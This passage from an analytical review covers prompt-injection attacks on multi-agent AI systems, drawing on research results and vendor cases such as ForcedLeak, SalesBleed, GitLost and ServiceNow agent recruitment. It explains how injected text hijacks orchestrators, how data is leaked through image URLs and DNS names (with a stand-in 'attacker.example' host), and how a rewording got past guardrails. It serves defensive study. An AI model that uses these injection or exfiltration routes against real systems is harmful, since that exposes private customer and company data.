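In *Multi-Agent Systems Execute Arbitrary Malicious Code*, Triedman, Jha and Shmatikov (2025) attacked teams of agents built with the open-source frameworks AutoGen, Crew AI and MetaGPT. In a typical team, separate agents read files, browse the web, write code and run it. An *orchestrator*, which is also a language model, usually decides which agent acts next.

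To make that decision, the orchestrator needs both content and status reports that show which steps failed and why. The attack exploits this with a web page or file whose text looks like an error message and presents running the attacker's program as the way around the error. The reading agent reports the error, and the orchestrator, which is meant to find another way when a step fails, tells the code-running agent to run the program. The reading agent has become a confused deputy, because the attacker's request now looks to the orchestrator like a report from a trusted agent.

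When a user asked a team of agents to open a malicious web page, the attacker's program ran in 45% to 64% of trials, depending on the orchestrator. These are the paper's reported averages across models, but averaging the per-model rates in the same table gives somewhat higher figures for most orchestrators. Three injection templates from earlier research succeeded in at most 1% of trials. GPT-4o never complied when the user asked it directly to run such code, but teams built on it ran the attacker's program in 58% to 90% of trials.

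Calling the agents in a fixed order, instead of letting the model choose the next one, didn't help. In one AutoGen configuration that does this, the attack still succeeded 58% of the time on average, because each agent can see part of what the others have reported.

One agent's refusal didn't reliably stop the team. In one trial, the coding agent refused to write the malicious program, so the file-reading agent wrote one itself, with a comment warning against running it. The code-running agent then ran it. In several other trials, the coding agent recognised the program as malicious and added warnings to the code, but reported success to the orchestrator, which ordered it to run the code.

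The agents in these teams had different tools, but no code checked whether a report justified a new instruction to the agent that ran programs. The only safeguard was the models' own judgement. Triedman and colleagues used three error messages written in advance, and an attacker who adapted the messages might have succeeded more often. The rates are weak evidence about current systems, because the models were versions of GPT-4o and Gemini 1.5, which are long out of date. Dividing the work didn't stop the attack, but the study didn't compare these teams with a single agent that held all the tools, so its results don't establish whether dividing the work made the attack easier.

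### Why securing each agent isn't enough

In Triedman and colleagues' attack, untrusted text changes which agents act and in what order. CaMeL prevents this within one agent by writing the program before any untrusted text arrives. Peters-Gill and colleagues got an injection in a database of job applicants past three CaMeL agents, but they also found that running CaMeL on each agent stops another attack, OMNI-Leak. In OMNI-Leak, an instruction in a public database directs the database agent to read a private one as well. The attack failed in all five trials, and the system still answered every ordinary query correctly.

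The two results differ because the database agent in OMNI-Leak reads the malicious text after it has written its program, while the notification agent in the job-applicant attack receives the text before it writes one.

Peters-Gill and colleagues show that this gap is general. They say a system has *control-flow integrity* if it follows only plans determined by the user's instruction and other trusted information. Under a mild assumption about what users can ask for, any hierarchy of two or more agents lacks this property if one of its tools returns untrusted data, even when each agent has the property individually. A designer therefore can't establish the property for the whole system by checking the agents one at a time, and also has to control what passes between them. The result doesn't imply that every request is dangerous.

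In both demonstrations, CaMeL's interpreter enforced a boundary inside each agent, but nothing enforced one between agents. The demonstrations used GPT-5.2, which OpenAI has since replaced, and neither involved an attacker who kept revising the injection.

### A request from a colleague

*The Dark Side of LLMs* (Lupinacci, Pironti and colleagues, 2025) compared three ways of getting an agent to install malware. In the first, a user asked for it directly. In the second, the agent retrieved a document with a hidden instruction while answering a harmless question. The third used two agents running on the same model. One agent answered questions from documents and could not use the computer's command line. It read the hidden instruction and passed the command to the other agent, which could run commands and was assigned to carry out the first agent's requests.

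They tested 18 models that were current in July 2025, with six prompts and up to three runs of each. A model counted as vulnerable if the malware ran even once. The last column of this table is a count of the results for each combination of model and prompt:

| Source of the command | Vulnerable models | Successful combinations |
|---|---|---|
| User | 17 of 18 | About 74% |
| Document | 15 of 18 | About 58% |
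| Another agent | 18 of 18 | About 81% |

The last column better shows the size of the effect, because a model that fails once in 18 attempts counts the same in the middle column as one that fails every time. Claude 4 Opus ran the malware for one of the six prompts when it read the document itself, and for five of the six when another agent passed on the command. Llama 3.3 went from none of the six prompts to five.

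Lupinacci and colleagues conclude that models trust other agents in a way that bypasses their normal safeguards. But the experiment changed more than the source of the request. In the tests with a user or a document, the command came with suspicious text that demanded immediate execution. The second agent in the two-agent test saw only the command, and its standing instructions described it as an assistant that other agents call on to complete operations. Some models may have refused because of the wording, not the source. To isolate the effect of trust in other agents, researchers would have to send the same bare command from a user.

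The result is worrying for security under either explanation. If the first agent removes the suspicious wording when it passes on a command, the second agent is less likely to recognise an attack than a single agent would be.

In a follow-up test, the attack's success depended on the second agent's tools. Lupinacci and colleagues gave three of the models a tool that checks whether a network address responds, instead of full command-line access. The malware didn't run in the two-agent system, because the second agent passed only the address to the tool. But it did run when the command came from a user or a document, because the models then passed extra text to the tool, which executed it. When the tool was a file-search program that can also start other programs, the attack again worked in the two-agent system on all three models.

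The network tool was safe in the two-agent system only because of how the models happened to use it. If its code had accepted only an address, the malware couldn't have run through it, whoever sent the request. The original system mainly divided work between the agents, and this restriction would have divided authority as well. Lupinacci and colleagues propose a program that checks each command before it runs, but leave building and testing it to future work.

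The experiments used fixed attacks, and newer models have replaced most of those tested. The failure rates may have changed, but the design flaw doesn't depend on them.

### From one agent to the whole team

An injection can also instruct an agent to pass it on. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) calls the spread of malicious instructions from agent to agent *cascading infection*. It credits Lee and Tiwari with the earlier term *prompt infection*, for text that makes each agent pass the attack to the next. An infected agent may rewrite the instructions as it passes them on, as some computer viruses change their code to avoid detection, so a filter that looks for the original wording could miss them.

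Paul and Nandy (2026), in *Beyond Single-Model Injection*, measured both attacks that spread between agents and attacks on the orchestrator. Their system analysed financial documents with six agents: an orchestrator, four specialists (retrieval, code, analysis and compliance) and one that wrote the output. They tried 14 kinds of attack, with 50 versions of each, and counted an attack as successful if the target agent did something outside its permitted role.

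Attacks from one agent to another succeeded 31% of the time. Attacks that cascaded through the orchestrator, such as by making it send work to the wrong agent or keep a compromised job running, succeeded 28% of the time. The 31% figure is hard to interpret because some of those attacks start with an agent that is already compromised. If it measures only the spread to a second agent, and compromising the first agent succeeds 43% of the time, the rate measured for malicious tool outputs, then about 13% of attacks would complete both steps.

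Before adding defences, Paul and Nandy relied on instructions telling the agents to reject unauthorised requests. They then tested four defences, separately and together. The table gives attack success rates in percent:

| Defence | From the user | From tool outputs | Between agents | Through the orchestrator |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Instructions only | 19 | 43 | 31 | 28 |
| Signed messages | 19 | 43 | 2.8 | 18 |
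| Filters at each agent's boundary | 8.4 | 9.5 | 31 | 22 |
| Tools restricted by role | 19 | 34 | 31 | 16 |
| Monitoring of message patterns | 14 | 38 | 24 | 4.5 |
| All four | 3.8 | 4.6 | 1.2 | 3.4 |

Restricting tools didn't reduce attacks between agents, possibly because an agent can do harm without using a tool. In the paper's opening example, a malicious tool output leads the compliance agent to approve a request, and the orchestrator acts on the approval without checking it. The compliance agent needs no dangerous tool for this because the other agents treat its report as permission, and restricting tools doesn't change that.

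The effect of signed messages is harder to explain. Each agent signs what it sends and records where the content came from, and recipients set aside unsigned messages. But an agent that has obeyed an injection can still sign its messages. Signing would therefore explain the fall from 31% to 2.8% only if most of the attacks relied on impersonation or recipients also acted on the recorded source. It is also odd that filtering every message between agents had no effect on attacks between them.

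Paul and Nandy's numbers have other problems. They report that the four defences together reduced the overall success rate from 31.2% to 4.2%, but the last row of their table averages about 3.2% when weighted by the number of attacks. A 2.8% success rate over 200 attempts between agents would be 5.6 successes, so the 2.8% must come from some other calculation. Each baseline figure is the highest of three models' rates. If the figures with defences are averages across models, the comparison exaggerates the improvement.

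The three models were GPT-4o, Claude 3.5 Sonnet and Llama 3 70B, all well out of date. Paul and Nandy had refined the attacks to get past the original instructions, but didn't adapt them to the new defences. They also don't report how many ordinary jobs the system completed with the defences on. The filter wrongly flagged 2.3% of harmless inputs. If that rate applies independently to each of the 15 messages in a typical job, about 30% of jobs would have at least one false alarm.

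Some attacks don't spread. In *An Exploration of Attacks on AI Agent Systems*, Qiao, Cabilangan and colleagues (2026) gave one of three agents in a group chat a secret and told the other two not to ask about it. Most attempts to extract the secret failed, and in the one case where the agent revealed it, neither of the others repeated it. One leak and two agents that could have passed it on are too few to rule out a high rate of spread. The attacker was also trying to extract the secret, and nothing suggests that the attack text told agents to copy that text.

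Qiao and colleagues ran each group-chat test only three to five times, on a small Llama 3 model that is now obsolete. Their other tests, on a hierarchy of agents using A2A, had mixed results. One prompt failed to extract a secret key in five single attempts, but repeating it up to 15 times worked in three of five trials. In another test, an agent had a tool that could read local files, and the only protection for sensitive files was an instruction not to open them. The agent read a protected file in two of five trials when asked plainly, and in all five when also told that the file was harmless.

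*ACIArena* (2026) is a benchmark dedicated to cascading injection, with 1,356 test cases and 28 attacks. It measures the usual attack success rate and also spread, which accounts for how many steps separate the malicious agent from the final answer. This second measure could distinguish systems where only the last agent is dangerous from systems where an attack can start anywhere.

### Does a central service lower the risk?

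*Agent-Canary-Mas* (Liu, Gai and colleagues, 2026) compares three ways of connecting agents. With A2A, agents contact each other directly. The Agent Network Protocol (ANP) is also decentralised and lets agents find and verify each other through published identities and service descriptions. The Bot Coordination Service (BCS) mediates between agents by keeping a central directory, managing their sessions and routing their messages, but it leaves them to decide whether to believe the messages.

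The attacker was a legitimate participant with valid credentials that changed one thing it was allowed to publish or send. In one example, a coordinator has to find out whether a batch of payments has been approved, and a dishonest service changes its own description so that the coordinator chooses it as the source. This is a *local success* for the attacker, but it causes harm only if a later agent accepts the service's answer and prepares the payments. That agent may instead check the approval records and hold the batch.

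The benchmark has 975 tasks in fields such as finance and healthcare, each in an honest and a malicious version. Liu and colleagues ran all of them with MiniMax-M3, GLM-5.2 and GPT-5.6 Terra, which are much newer than the models in the other attack studies. The table gives the range across the three models. The last column is an estimate, made by multiplying the two published rates for each of five classes of attack and averaging the results. It is approximate because those rates are already averages.

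| Protocol | Local success | Harm after a local success | Harm overall |
|---|---|---|---|
| A2A, direct | 98–100% | 83–86% | 81–85% |
| ANP, decentralised | 87–92% | 63–81% | 53–74% |
| BCS, central service | 72–91% | 82–97% | 57–88% |

The central service in BCS didn't clearly lower the risk. Fewer attacks achieved local success than under A2A, but those that did were often at least as likely to cause harm. Estimated overall harm was much lower under BCS than under A2A with GPT-5.6 Terra (57% versus 81%) but slightly higher with GLM-5.2 (88% versus 85%). ANP, which has no central service, did better than BCS with all three models.

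Attacks on routing show why local success rates alone are misleading. Under BCS, only 48% to 67% of attempts to misdirect a message or task worked. For two of the three models, these were the lowest rates of any class of attack. But every successful attempt led to harm, because later agents rarely corrected a task once it was on the wrong path.

Central coordination made it easier to find the responsible agent afterwards. Liu and colleagues asked a model to identify that agent from each protocol's own records and scored its answers with F1, which penalises both missing a responsible agent and blaming an innocent one. The scores were 69% for BCS, 20% for A2A and zero for ANP. With extra records linking each message to the agent that used it and to the result, all three scored above 92%.

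### Checking authority at each handover

Liu and colleagues also tested the Guard, a mediator that checks both a message's route and whether its sender has authority for the way another agent is about to use it. For example, the Guard can let an agent use a supplier's report as information but not as approval for a payment. This restriction stays with the report when it passes to the next agent. The Guard applies fixed checks first, and a language model reviews the unclear cases.

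On 195 finance tasks with MiniMax-M3, the Guard reduced local success from 86.1% to 53.8%, and harm after a local success from 65.5% to 31.2%. Estimated as before, overall harm fell from about 66% to 9% under A2A, from 61% to 14% under BCS, and from 46% to 25% under ANP. Harm fell at least as much under A2A as under BCS, so checks on authority can work without a central service.

The Guard was more effective against routing attacks under BCS, though, because it could refuse a route before the central service sent the message. It cut the attacks' success rate from 66.7% to zero under BCS, but only from 90.7% to 70.7% under A2A.

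The share of task pairs that ran to completion fell from about 99.8% to 95.1% on average, and to 76.7% for one class of task under BCS. To count as complete, a pair only needed both versions to finish with a result that could be judged, so the loss of correct work may be larger. The attacks didn't adapt to the Guard. The same model ran the agents, reviewed the unclear cases and judged many of the outcomes, so a message that misled the agents might also have misled the reviewer and the judge.

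Under BCS with the Guard on, 69% of attacks that made a message seem more authoritative than it was still achieved local success, and 40% of those led to harm. The central service could control where such a message went, but recognising a false approval required checking it against a source that the attacker didn't control.

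## How has separation fared in deployed products?

The researchers in those experiments built or configured the multi-agent systems themselves. In a commercial product, a boundary also depends on default settings, old lists of approved addresses, and how each customer connects the agent to its own data. Security companies found the best-documented failures by attacking such products, then published their methods. These companies often sell protection against the same attacks, so they have reason both to look hard for flaws and to describe them in alarming terms.

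### A web form and an expired domain

Agentforce is a Salesforce platform for building agents that work with a company's records of its customers, prospects and deals. Another Salesforce feature, Web-to-Lead, puts a form on the company's public website and stores whatever a visitor types as a new sales lead. The security company Noma found that a visitor could use this form to steal other prospects' details, an attack it called ForcedLeak (Noma's report, reposted by Nytro, 2025, in *ForcedLeak*).

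Noma first looked for a field with enough room for instructions. The fields for names, company and email address accepted 40 to 80 characters, but the description field accepted 42,000. Noma put four numbered requests there. One asked what colour red and yellow make, another asked for the email addresses of the company's leads, and the last told the agent to end its answer with an image whose web address contained those email addresses.

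The leak began only when an employee asked Agentforce to check the lead, answer its questions and draft a reply. The agent looked up the addresses and put the image in its answer. Loading the image sent the addresses to Noma's server. Two years earlier, Willison had forbidden images in his quarantined model's output to prevent this kind of leak.

Salesforce did restrict the last step by letting its pages load images only from approved domains. But the registration for one of them, `my-salesforce-cms.com`, had expired, and Noma bought the domain for $5.

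The visitor had no Salesforce account and never dealt with the agent directly, but the agent treated the visitor's stored text as instructions. Because one agent was both exposed and trusted, ForcedLeak is an example of combined roles rather than a failure of role separation. The list of domains was the last barrier between a public form and the customer database.

Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025. Salesforce regained control of the domain and, from 8 September, restricted its agents to an allowlist of trusted web addresses. According to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*, administrators must add every outside domain their agents need. Noma's attack was a demonstration. Salesforce confirmed the repair to The Register (2025) but declined to say whether anyone had abused the flaw, and this remains unclear.

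In September 2026, another security company, Zenity, published SalesBleed, an attack that starts with the same form. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk*, the injected text made an agent look up company names and deal sizes and send them out through DNS, the system that translates domain names into network addresses. In this kind of leak, the attacker puts the data into a domain name, such as `acme-50000.attacker.example`. Looking up that name sends the data to a server the attacker controls, even if no page or image loads.

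SalesBleed bypassed the allowlist control that Salesforce had begun enforcing after ForcedLeak. Zenity reported it in June, and Salesforce finished fixing the bypass on 18 August. Both of Salesforce's announced repairs blocked a route for sending data out, so an attacker could still look for another. Zenity noted that its injection could have requested anything the agent's query tool could reach. Had the tool been limited to the lead being processed, the other records would have been safe in both attacks, regardless of how the data was sent out.

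An allowlist can also fail because an approved item no longer does what the approver expected. Help Net Security's *Prompt injection still drives most agentic AI security failures in production* (2026) describes such a flaw in Cursor, a programming tool whose agent can run commands. An attacker who tampered with the environment where the commands ran could make an ordinary approved command, such as `git branch`, deliver malicious code. The allowlist made the attack easier because Cursor ran approved commands without asking the user.

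### A public question about a private repository

GitHub, which hosts software projects in public and private repositories, lets teams write automated workflows in plain language for an agent to carry out. In July 2026, Levi's *GitLost* described an attack on one such workflow. When someone assigned an issue (a question or bug report), the agent read it and posted a comment in reply. The agent could also read the organisation's other repositories, including private ones.

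Levi, who works for Noma, opened an issue in a public repository and wrote it as a plausible request from a head of sales who had just met a customer. GitHub's automation assigned the issue, and the agent fetched a file from a private repository and posted its contents in a public comment. The attack required no credentials or programming skills. Levi used test repositories, so it harmed nobody.

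GitHub's access rules kept public readers out of private repositories, but the agent had legitimate access to both the private repositories and the public one. Its job included posting public comments, so GitLost, unlike ForcedLeak, did not need an obscure route for sending data out, and an allowlist of web addresses would not have helped. GitHub had guardrails against such leaks, but Levi kept rewording the request and found that adding "Additionally" got the agent to comply. A credential that could read only the public repository would have stopped the attack regardless of the wording. A workflow that needs private code could send its answers to a private channel.

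### Agents that recruit each other

ServiceNow's Now Assist, a platform for agents that handle office and IT work, comes closer to role separation because it divides tools among specialised agents. But those agents can call on each other for help, and the security company AppOmni found that an outsider could use text to exploit this (The Hacker News, November 2025).

In Now Assist, one agent can recruit another if the underlying language model supports *agent discovery*, both agents belong to the same team, and the second agent is marked as discoverable. All three conditions hold by default. The product puts agents deployed to the same chat assistant in one team, often without the administrator noticing. If an agent can't finish a task alone, an orchestrator looks for another agent on the team that can.

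Aaron Costello, then AppOmni's head of security research, tested this with two of ServiceNow's ready-made agents, which only an administrator could use. One read and summarised incident tickets, and the other could read, create and update many kinds of records. Costello created an ordinary user account that could file tickets but couldn't read anyone else's.

As that user, Costello filed a ticket instructing any agent that read it to copy the text of a confidential ticket into this one before continuing, and to look for another agent if it couldn't do so itself. When the administrator triggered the reading agent, it enlisted the record-keeping agent, which copied the confidential text into the ordinary user's ticket, where that user could read it. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. In other tests, Costello got agents to make a malicious user an administrator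 and to email records outside the company.

The separation relied on the false assumption that an agent without a tool can't do what the tool does. The platform divided the work among agents without dividing the authority, as in the teams that Triedman and colleagues attacked. Both agents also acted with the permissions of the administrator who had started the conversation, although the instructions came from an ordinary user with far fewer. A check like the one in FIDES would have blocked the copy, because that user could read the destination but wasn't permitted to read the source.

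ServiceNow told AppOmni that it intended these behaviours, and updated its documentation. Costello partly agreed, telling The Hacker News that "it isn't a bug in the AI" but a result of default settings. Discovery is a reasonable feature, since agents that can't help each other are less useful. The defaults are harder to defend, because an administrator who doesn't know two agents are on the same team has no reason to separate them.

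AppOmni recommends dividing agents into separate teams, each with only those needed for one task, and requiring a person's approval before tools change records or send email. An attacker who hijacks the reading agent can then use only the tools in its team. Approval works only if the administrator notices that a request to categorise a ticket has led to an attempt to overwrite it. AppOmni also recommends continuous monitoring and sells a product for it. AppOmni's attack was a demonstration, like Unit 42's session smuggling, but it used a vendor's own agents and default discovery settings.

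### Chrome's checking model

Some vendors have built separation into their products from the start. Google's Chrome browser has an agent that reads web pages and clicks and types for the user, often on sites where the user is logged in. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) explains how Google protects the agent.

Chrome reverses Willison's arrangement. Its planning model reads the pages, and a second model, the *User Alignment Critic*, checks whether each proposed action serves the user's goal before the browser carries it out. The critic receives a description of the action but doesn't read the pages. If it vetoes the action, the planner gets feedback and tries again. After repeated failures, the planner can hand control back to the user.

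This lets the agent react to what it finds, which is difficult for systems that fix the plan in advance. But the critic has to recognise a harmful action from very little information. It has a good chance of noticing if a user who asked for a T-shirt ends up on a banking site, but it is less likely to notice if an injection on a shopping page steers the agent to an overpriced T-shirt, because adding that shirt to the cart still fits the user's goal. Parker also writes that the critic sees no "unfiltered" untrustworthy content, which leaves open how much filtered text, such as a product name, might reach it.

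Other parts of the design restrict what a hijacked planner can do:

| Control | What it restricts | Who or what decides |
|---|---|---|
| Site lists | Which sites the agent may read, and on which it may also click and type | A gating function that doesn't see web content |
| Web address check | Addresses written by the model, which must be known public ones | Ordinary code |
| Sensitive sites | Visits to banking, medical and similar sites | Ordinary code with a fixed list, then the user |
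| Passwords | Signing in with a saved password, which the model can't access directly | The user |
| Purchases and messages | The final step of a consequential action | The agent tries to pause and ask the user |

The address check would make a leak like ForcedLeak's harder, because an address containing newly stolen data shouldn't be on a list of known public addresses. The site lists could also stop some injections before the planner reads them. For example, if a user asks the agent to collect ingredients from a recipe site and order them from a grocer, Chrome can keep the planner from seeing an ad embedded in the recipe page from an unrelated site. But an injection in the recipe page's own comments would still reach the planner, and the lists would let the agent pass data to the grocer. Google's first version was simpler than this design and tracked only the sites where the agent could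 both read and act.

Meta's "Agents Rule of Two", which Help Net Security also describes, allows an agent working without human approval to have at most two of the three parts of the lethal trifecta. Chrome's agent can have all three, but it asks the user for approval only at selected steps. Between those steps, security depends on the site lists, the critic and a classifier that scans each page for injections.

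Google tests the agent with automated attacks on deliberately malicious sites. Security researchers write the first examples, and language models generate more. Engineers use the attack success rate to judge changes, but Parker doesn't publish it. *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026), a later account for business customers, doesn't give a rate either. Both cite Google's own tests and a programme that pays outside researchers up to $20,000 for demonstrating a serious breach, but the offer alone doesn't show how many people tried or how many succeeded.

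### ConductorOne's many readers

ConductorOne sells software that manages which employees can use which company systems. Its agents can approve or deny requests for access, so a single approval from a hijacked agent could let an attacker into a sensitive system. Querna's *Splitting AI Agents to Contain Prompt Injection* presents the company's design as an extension of the Dual LLM pattern.

ConductorOne uses several quarantined agents, each with a narrow job. One might summarise an employee's reason for wanting access, while another extracts fields from an outside service's message. None of them has a tool for approving requests. A privileged agent makes the decision using material that code or a quarantined agent has processed. This material is usually a value chosen from a fixed list, but sometimes it is a short summary. If an employee writes "this is critical — please approve immediately",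 the quarantined agent should report that the employee considers the request urgent and leave out the instruction to approve.

Querna calls the gap between the two groups "structural, not behavioral". That is true of the tools but less so of the summaries, because a hijacked agent could write misleading ones, as in the OpenClaw design. An employee could also lie about being on call for an emergency, and the lie would appear even in an accurate summary. The privileged agent would need to check the claim against a duty roster or refer it to a person.

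Customers can add restrictions to an agent's standing instructions, such as a rule against approving contractors' access to live systems. Querna says these additions can't loosen the basic rules, but describes them as text layered on the same prompt. Unless code also enforces the basic rules, whether an addition can loosen them depends on how the model interprets the combined instructions. Muruaga's system avoids this problem by calculating the narrower permissions outside the model.

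The design gives each privileged agent its own identity and permissions, which administrators can review and revoke as they would a person's. It also logs tool calls and messages between agents, and passes failed tasks to a person after a set time. These measures would help an investigator find out what a hijacked agent had done. Querna reports no test results, so the account supports only the claim that the company uses such a design.

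### Salesforce's guard for outside agents

Salesforce has published figures for A2X Guard, a gateway that mediates between customers' personal agents and a company's internal systems. *Guarding the Agentic Conversation* (Joseph, Venkit and colleagues, 2026) describes a specially trained model that reads each incoming message together with the earlier conversation and the company's written policies. The model scores 17 kinds of risk, and the gateway then passes the message, blocks it or holds it for a person to review. Reading the whole conversation helps the model detect gradual escalation, such as when an agent claims a manager's approval and then asks for a larger refund.

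Salesforce tested the guard on 391 conversations between agents, with 5,212 messages and 1,608 policy violations:

| Measure | GPT-6 Luna as a judge | A2X Guard |
|---|---|---|
| Violations caught | 79% | 75% |
| Harmless messages flagged | About 33% | About 2.3% |
| Time per message | About 800 ms | 43–68 ms |

The guard's low rate of false alarms matters because false alarms add up over a conversation. Conversations in the test average about 13 messages. If all 13 are harmless and errors are independent, the guard flags at least one message in about 26% of conversations, while the general-purpose judge does so in over 99%. A company that had to review nearly every conversation would probably switch the judge off.

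The guard still missed a quarter of the violations, or about 400. That may be acceptable for a layer in front of a broker with strict limits on refunds, but not for the only barrier to a customer's bank details. Salesforce was also testing its own product. Because the guard checks conversations with outside agents, these results don't show whether it would have caught ForcedLeak, which arrived through a web form.

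### What case reports cannot show

Case reports describe attacks that worked but usually don't include their success rates. Levi tried several wordings before finding one that got past GitHub's guardrails. Any attacker could repeat the attack if it succeeded once in five attempts, but if it succeeded once in 5,000, GitHub might notice the failed attempts first.

Counts of published flaws don't provide a failure rate either. Help Net Security reports that a 2026 survey of 53 agent projects by OWASP, a software security non-profit, found 57 security advisories for the workflow platform n8n, 22 for Claude Code and 15 for AutoGPT. A project may have many advisories because it has many flaws, because many people examine it, or because its developers disclose more. The counts also don't distinguish products that separate roles from those that don't. A fair comparison would need to run the same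 attacks against both kinds of system, as in the OpenClaw experiment.

Some attacks in the survey were real, but they often targeted the software around the agent. In one, attackers compromised the LiteLLM gateway, and users downloaded the malicious version nearly 47,000 times in three hours. In another, the developer of `postmark-mcp`, a package for connecting agents to a service, released 15 clean versions before adding a line that stole data. Neither attack relied on manipulating an agent that reads strangers' messages, so neither tests whether separating that agent from the data works.

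Public reports also leave out attacks that separation stopped without anyone noticing. If one of ConductorOne's quarantined agents reads an injected instruction to approve a request, the agent can't carry it out, and the only trace may be an odd summary in a log. Successful thefts can go unnoticed too. In the ForcedLeak scenario, for example, an employee might see only an answer to a sales enquiry. Public cases therefore aren't enough to tell whether separation usually works.

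Vendors could publish some of the missing numbers, such as how often Chrome's critic vetoes an action. But that figure would include the planner's ordinary mistakes as well as attacks, and would leave out every attack the critic approved.

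## What does separation cost, and when should a designer use it?

A company thinking of splitting an agent can estimate the drawbacks in advance, though it can't look up how often split agents fail in practice. The largest drawback is often that more tasks fail. CaMeL completed about half as many banking tasks with its policies on as with them off, and the sandbox in Jing's four-role design broke 11% of ordinary operations. The effect varies widely with the kind of work. Compared with an undefended agent, AgentSandbox's completion rate was 7.5 percentage points lower on office tasks but 5 points higher on travel tasks. Some tasks fail because a policy blocks a legitimate action, and others because the agent that acts never receives information it needs, such as the exact wording of an error message.

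Extra checks also take time. In published tests, brokers written in ordinary code typically delayed an action by less than 150 milliseconds, while a general-purpose model took about 800 milliseconds to check one message. Either delay would matter little to a purchasing agent that waits hours for a quote. On a programming task with 100 actions, an 800-millisecond check before each action would add 80 seconds.

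Someone also has to write the policies and keep them up to date. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes sandboxing as safe but high-maintenance, because each new capability needs configuring. Users who write their own rules often write loose ones. By June 2026, almost half the people using the command-line version of Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, had created rules that let some commands run without their approval. Many of those rules allowed any program in a language such as Python, which is almost the same as allowing every command.

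### Approval requests that nobody reads

A designer can avoid writing some policies by asking the owner to approve each action. Willison expected owners to stop reading such requests. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approved 97% of these requests, but most were probably harmless, so this figure alone doesn't show that users were careless.

Anthropic commissioned an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through a coding session, the text of one permission request changed to a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more earlier requests.

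The testers were not working on their own projects, so they may have been less careful than real owners. Anthropic also had an interest in the result, because it was replacing most of these requests with auto mode, an automated check that blocked 89% of the same commands. But even owners three times as careful as the testers would have approved most of the dangerous commands.

Users seem to read requests more carefully when they are rarer and more substantial. They rejected 39% of the plans Claude Code presented for approval, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. This suggests that they read the plans, but it doesn't show that they would notice an attack, because they may reject plans for reasons unrelated to security. The Frontier Model Forum warns that requests people click through can create an illusion of oversight, and that reviewing every output becomes impractical when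 many agents work in parallel.

Even if automated checks work much better than people, a test of Claude's auto mode gives little evidence that they let a designer keep a single agent instead of separating roles. Anthropic commissioned the test from Trajectory Labs, an outside evaluator, and none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three current Claude models running auto mode. But attacks succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average against Anthropic's latest models with the permission checks off, so the result reflects the models' own resistance more than the protection auto mode adds. The evaluators had also optimised the attacks against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7. On the same scenarios, attacks against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 19.03% of the time when it had full access and 5.83% when its own automatic reviewer was on.

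Willison (2026), in *30 posts tagged "lethal-trifecta"*, accepts that auto mode is better than constant requests but wants more independent confirmation. He doubts that any version could stop a malicious software package whose instructions tell the agent to download some files with a particular tool before running the tests. The tool actually steals data, but the step looks like normal programming work. He would rather run agents without access to data or tools that could do harm.

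### Sending only what the trusted agent lacks

Keeping the trusted agent away from outside text limits what it can do, because it often needs some of what the exposed agent has read. To fix a bug, for example, a programming agent has to know what the bug is, and a stranger may have written the bug report. Hu and colleagues tested an agent that could see a project's code but received nothing from the report, and it fixed none of 232 bugs. This restriction was harsher than Willison's Dual LLM pattern, which can at least pass values by name, so the result doesn't show how well that pattern would do.

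Twin Agent, published in July 2026, borrows an idea from video compression. A video file can store only the difference, called the *residual*, between a frame and what the player could predict from earlier frames. In Twin Agent, the Safe Agent already has the code, its own past commands and their results. The Explore Agent sees all of this as well as the bug report, so its messages can leave out everything the Safe Agent already has or can find for itself.

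Let *T* be the trusted material, *U* the untrusted material and *I* the history of the Safe Agent's work. An undefended agent would choose the action *π(T, U, I)*. The Safe Agent has a hint *H* in place of *U*, and chooses *π*ₛ*(T, H, I)*. The ideal hint solves this problem:

*minimise D(π*ₛ*(T, H, I), π(T, U, I)), with length(H) ≤ b*

*D* measures how much the two actions differ, and *b* is the maximum length of the hint. The software doesn't actually solve this equation. It approximates the solution by instructing the Explore Agent to send only missing facts. Each step of a bug fix works as follows:

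1. The Explore Agent reads the report and the work so far, and writes down the command it would run next. The system never runs this command.
2. If the Safe Agent would need a fact from the report to choose the same command, the Explore Agent writes a hint of up to 100 characters, such as "The crash happens only when the date field is empty". Otherwise it sends nothing.
3. A language model acting as a detector blocks the hint if it looks like an injection.
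4. The Safe Agent, whose standing instructions describe hints as untrusted background, runs one command. Both agents see the result.

The hint is still free text. A hundred characters can carry up to about 657 bits, and `rm main.py`, which deletes a file, takes only ten characters. A command can therefore fit easily within the limit, though there is little room for persuasion. Hu and colleagues argue that limiting persuasion is enough because the strongest current models follow only long injections that gradually persuade them. In their tests, attacks became more successful as the limit rose from 50 to 200 characters. Bug fixing also improved, although they measured that on only 20 bugs.

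The main tests used fixed attacks. The table shows percentages for the undefended agent and then for Twin Agent:

| Test | Model | Tasks completed | Attacks succeeding |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bug fixing (SWE-bench) | GPT-5.2 | 61.2 → 62.5 | 97.0 → 0.0 |
| AgentDojo | Gemini 2.5 Flash | 61.9 → 62.9 | 41.5 → 0.1 |
| Customer records and finance (DecodingTrust-Agent) | GPT-5.2 | 95.0 → 95.0 | 10.0 → 3.3 |
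| The same | Gemini 3.5 Flash | 96.7 → 93.3 | 26.7 → 3.3 |

Twin Agent completed about as many tasks as the undefended agent. In the same comparison, CaMeL completed 30.9% of AgentDojo tasks, though it had fewer retries than its designers allowed. On AgentDojo's Slack tasks, Twin Agent completed 14 (66.7%), compared with 19 (90.5%) for the undefended agent, but gains on the travel and banking tasks offset this loss in the average. Slack tasks may need more outside text than fits in the hints, which the test limited to 200 characters.

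Twin Agent cost about twice as much per bug as the undefended agent. Hu and colleagues report no figures for delay, but before every action the Safe Agent has to wait for a hint or a decision not to send one.

### If short injections start to work

Hu and colleagues also attacked their own design using their knowledge of how it worked. They had a model rewrite malicious hints up to 100 times, using feedback from the Safe Agent and the detector. They then planted an instruction in each bug report telling the Explore Agent to copy one of these hints word for word, and it did so every time. One hint claimed that `main.py` failed to load because a required string was missing from the end of the file. The attacker's goal was to get that string added, but the hint was written as a false explanation of the bug rather than an obvious injection.

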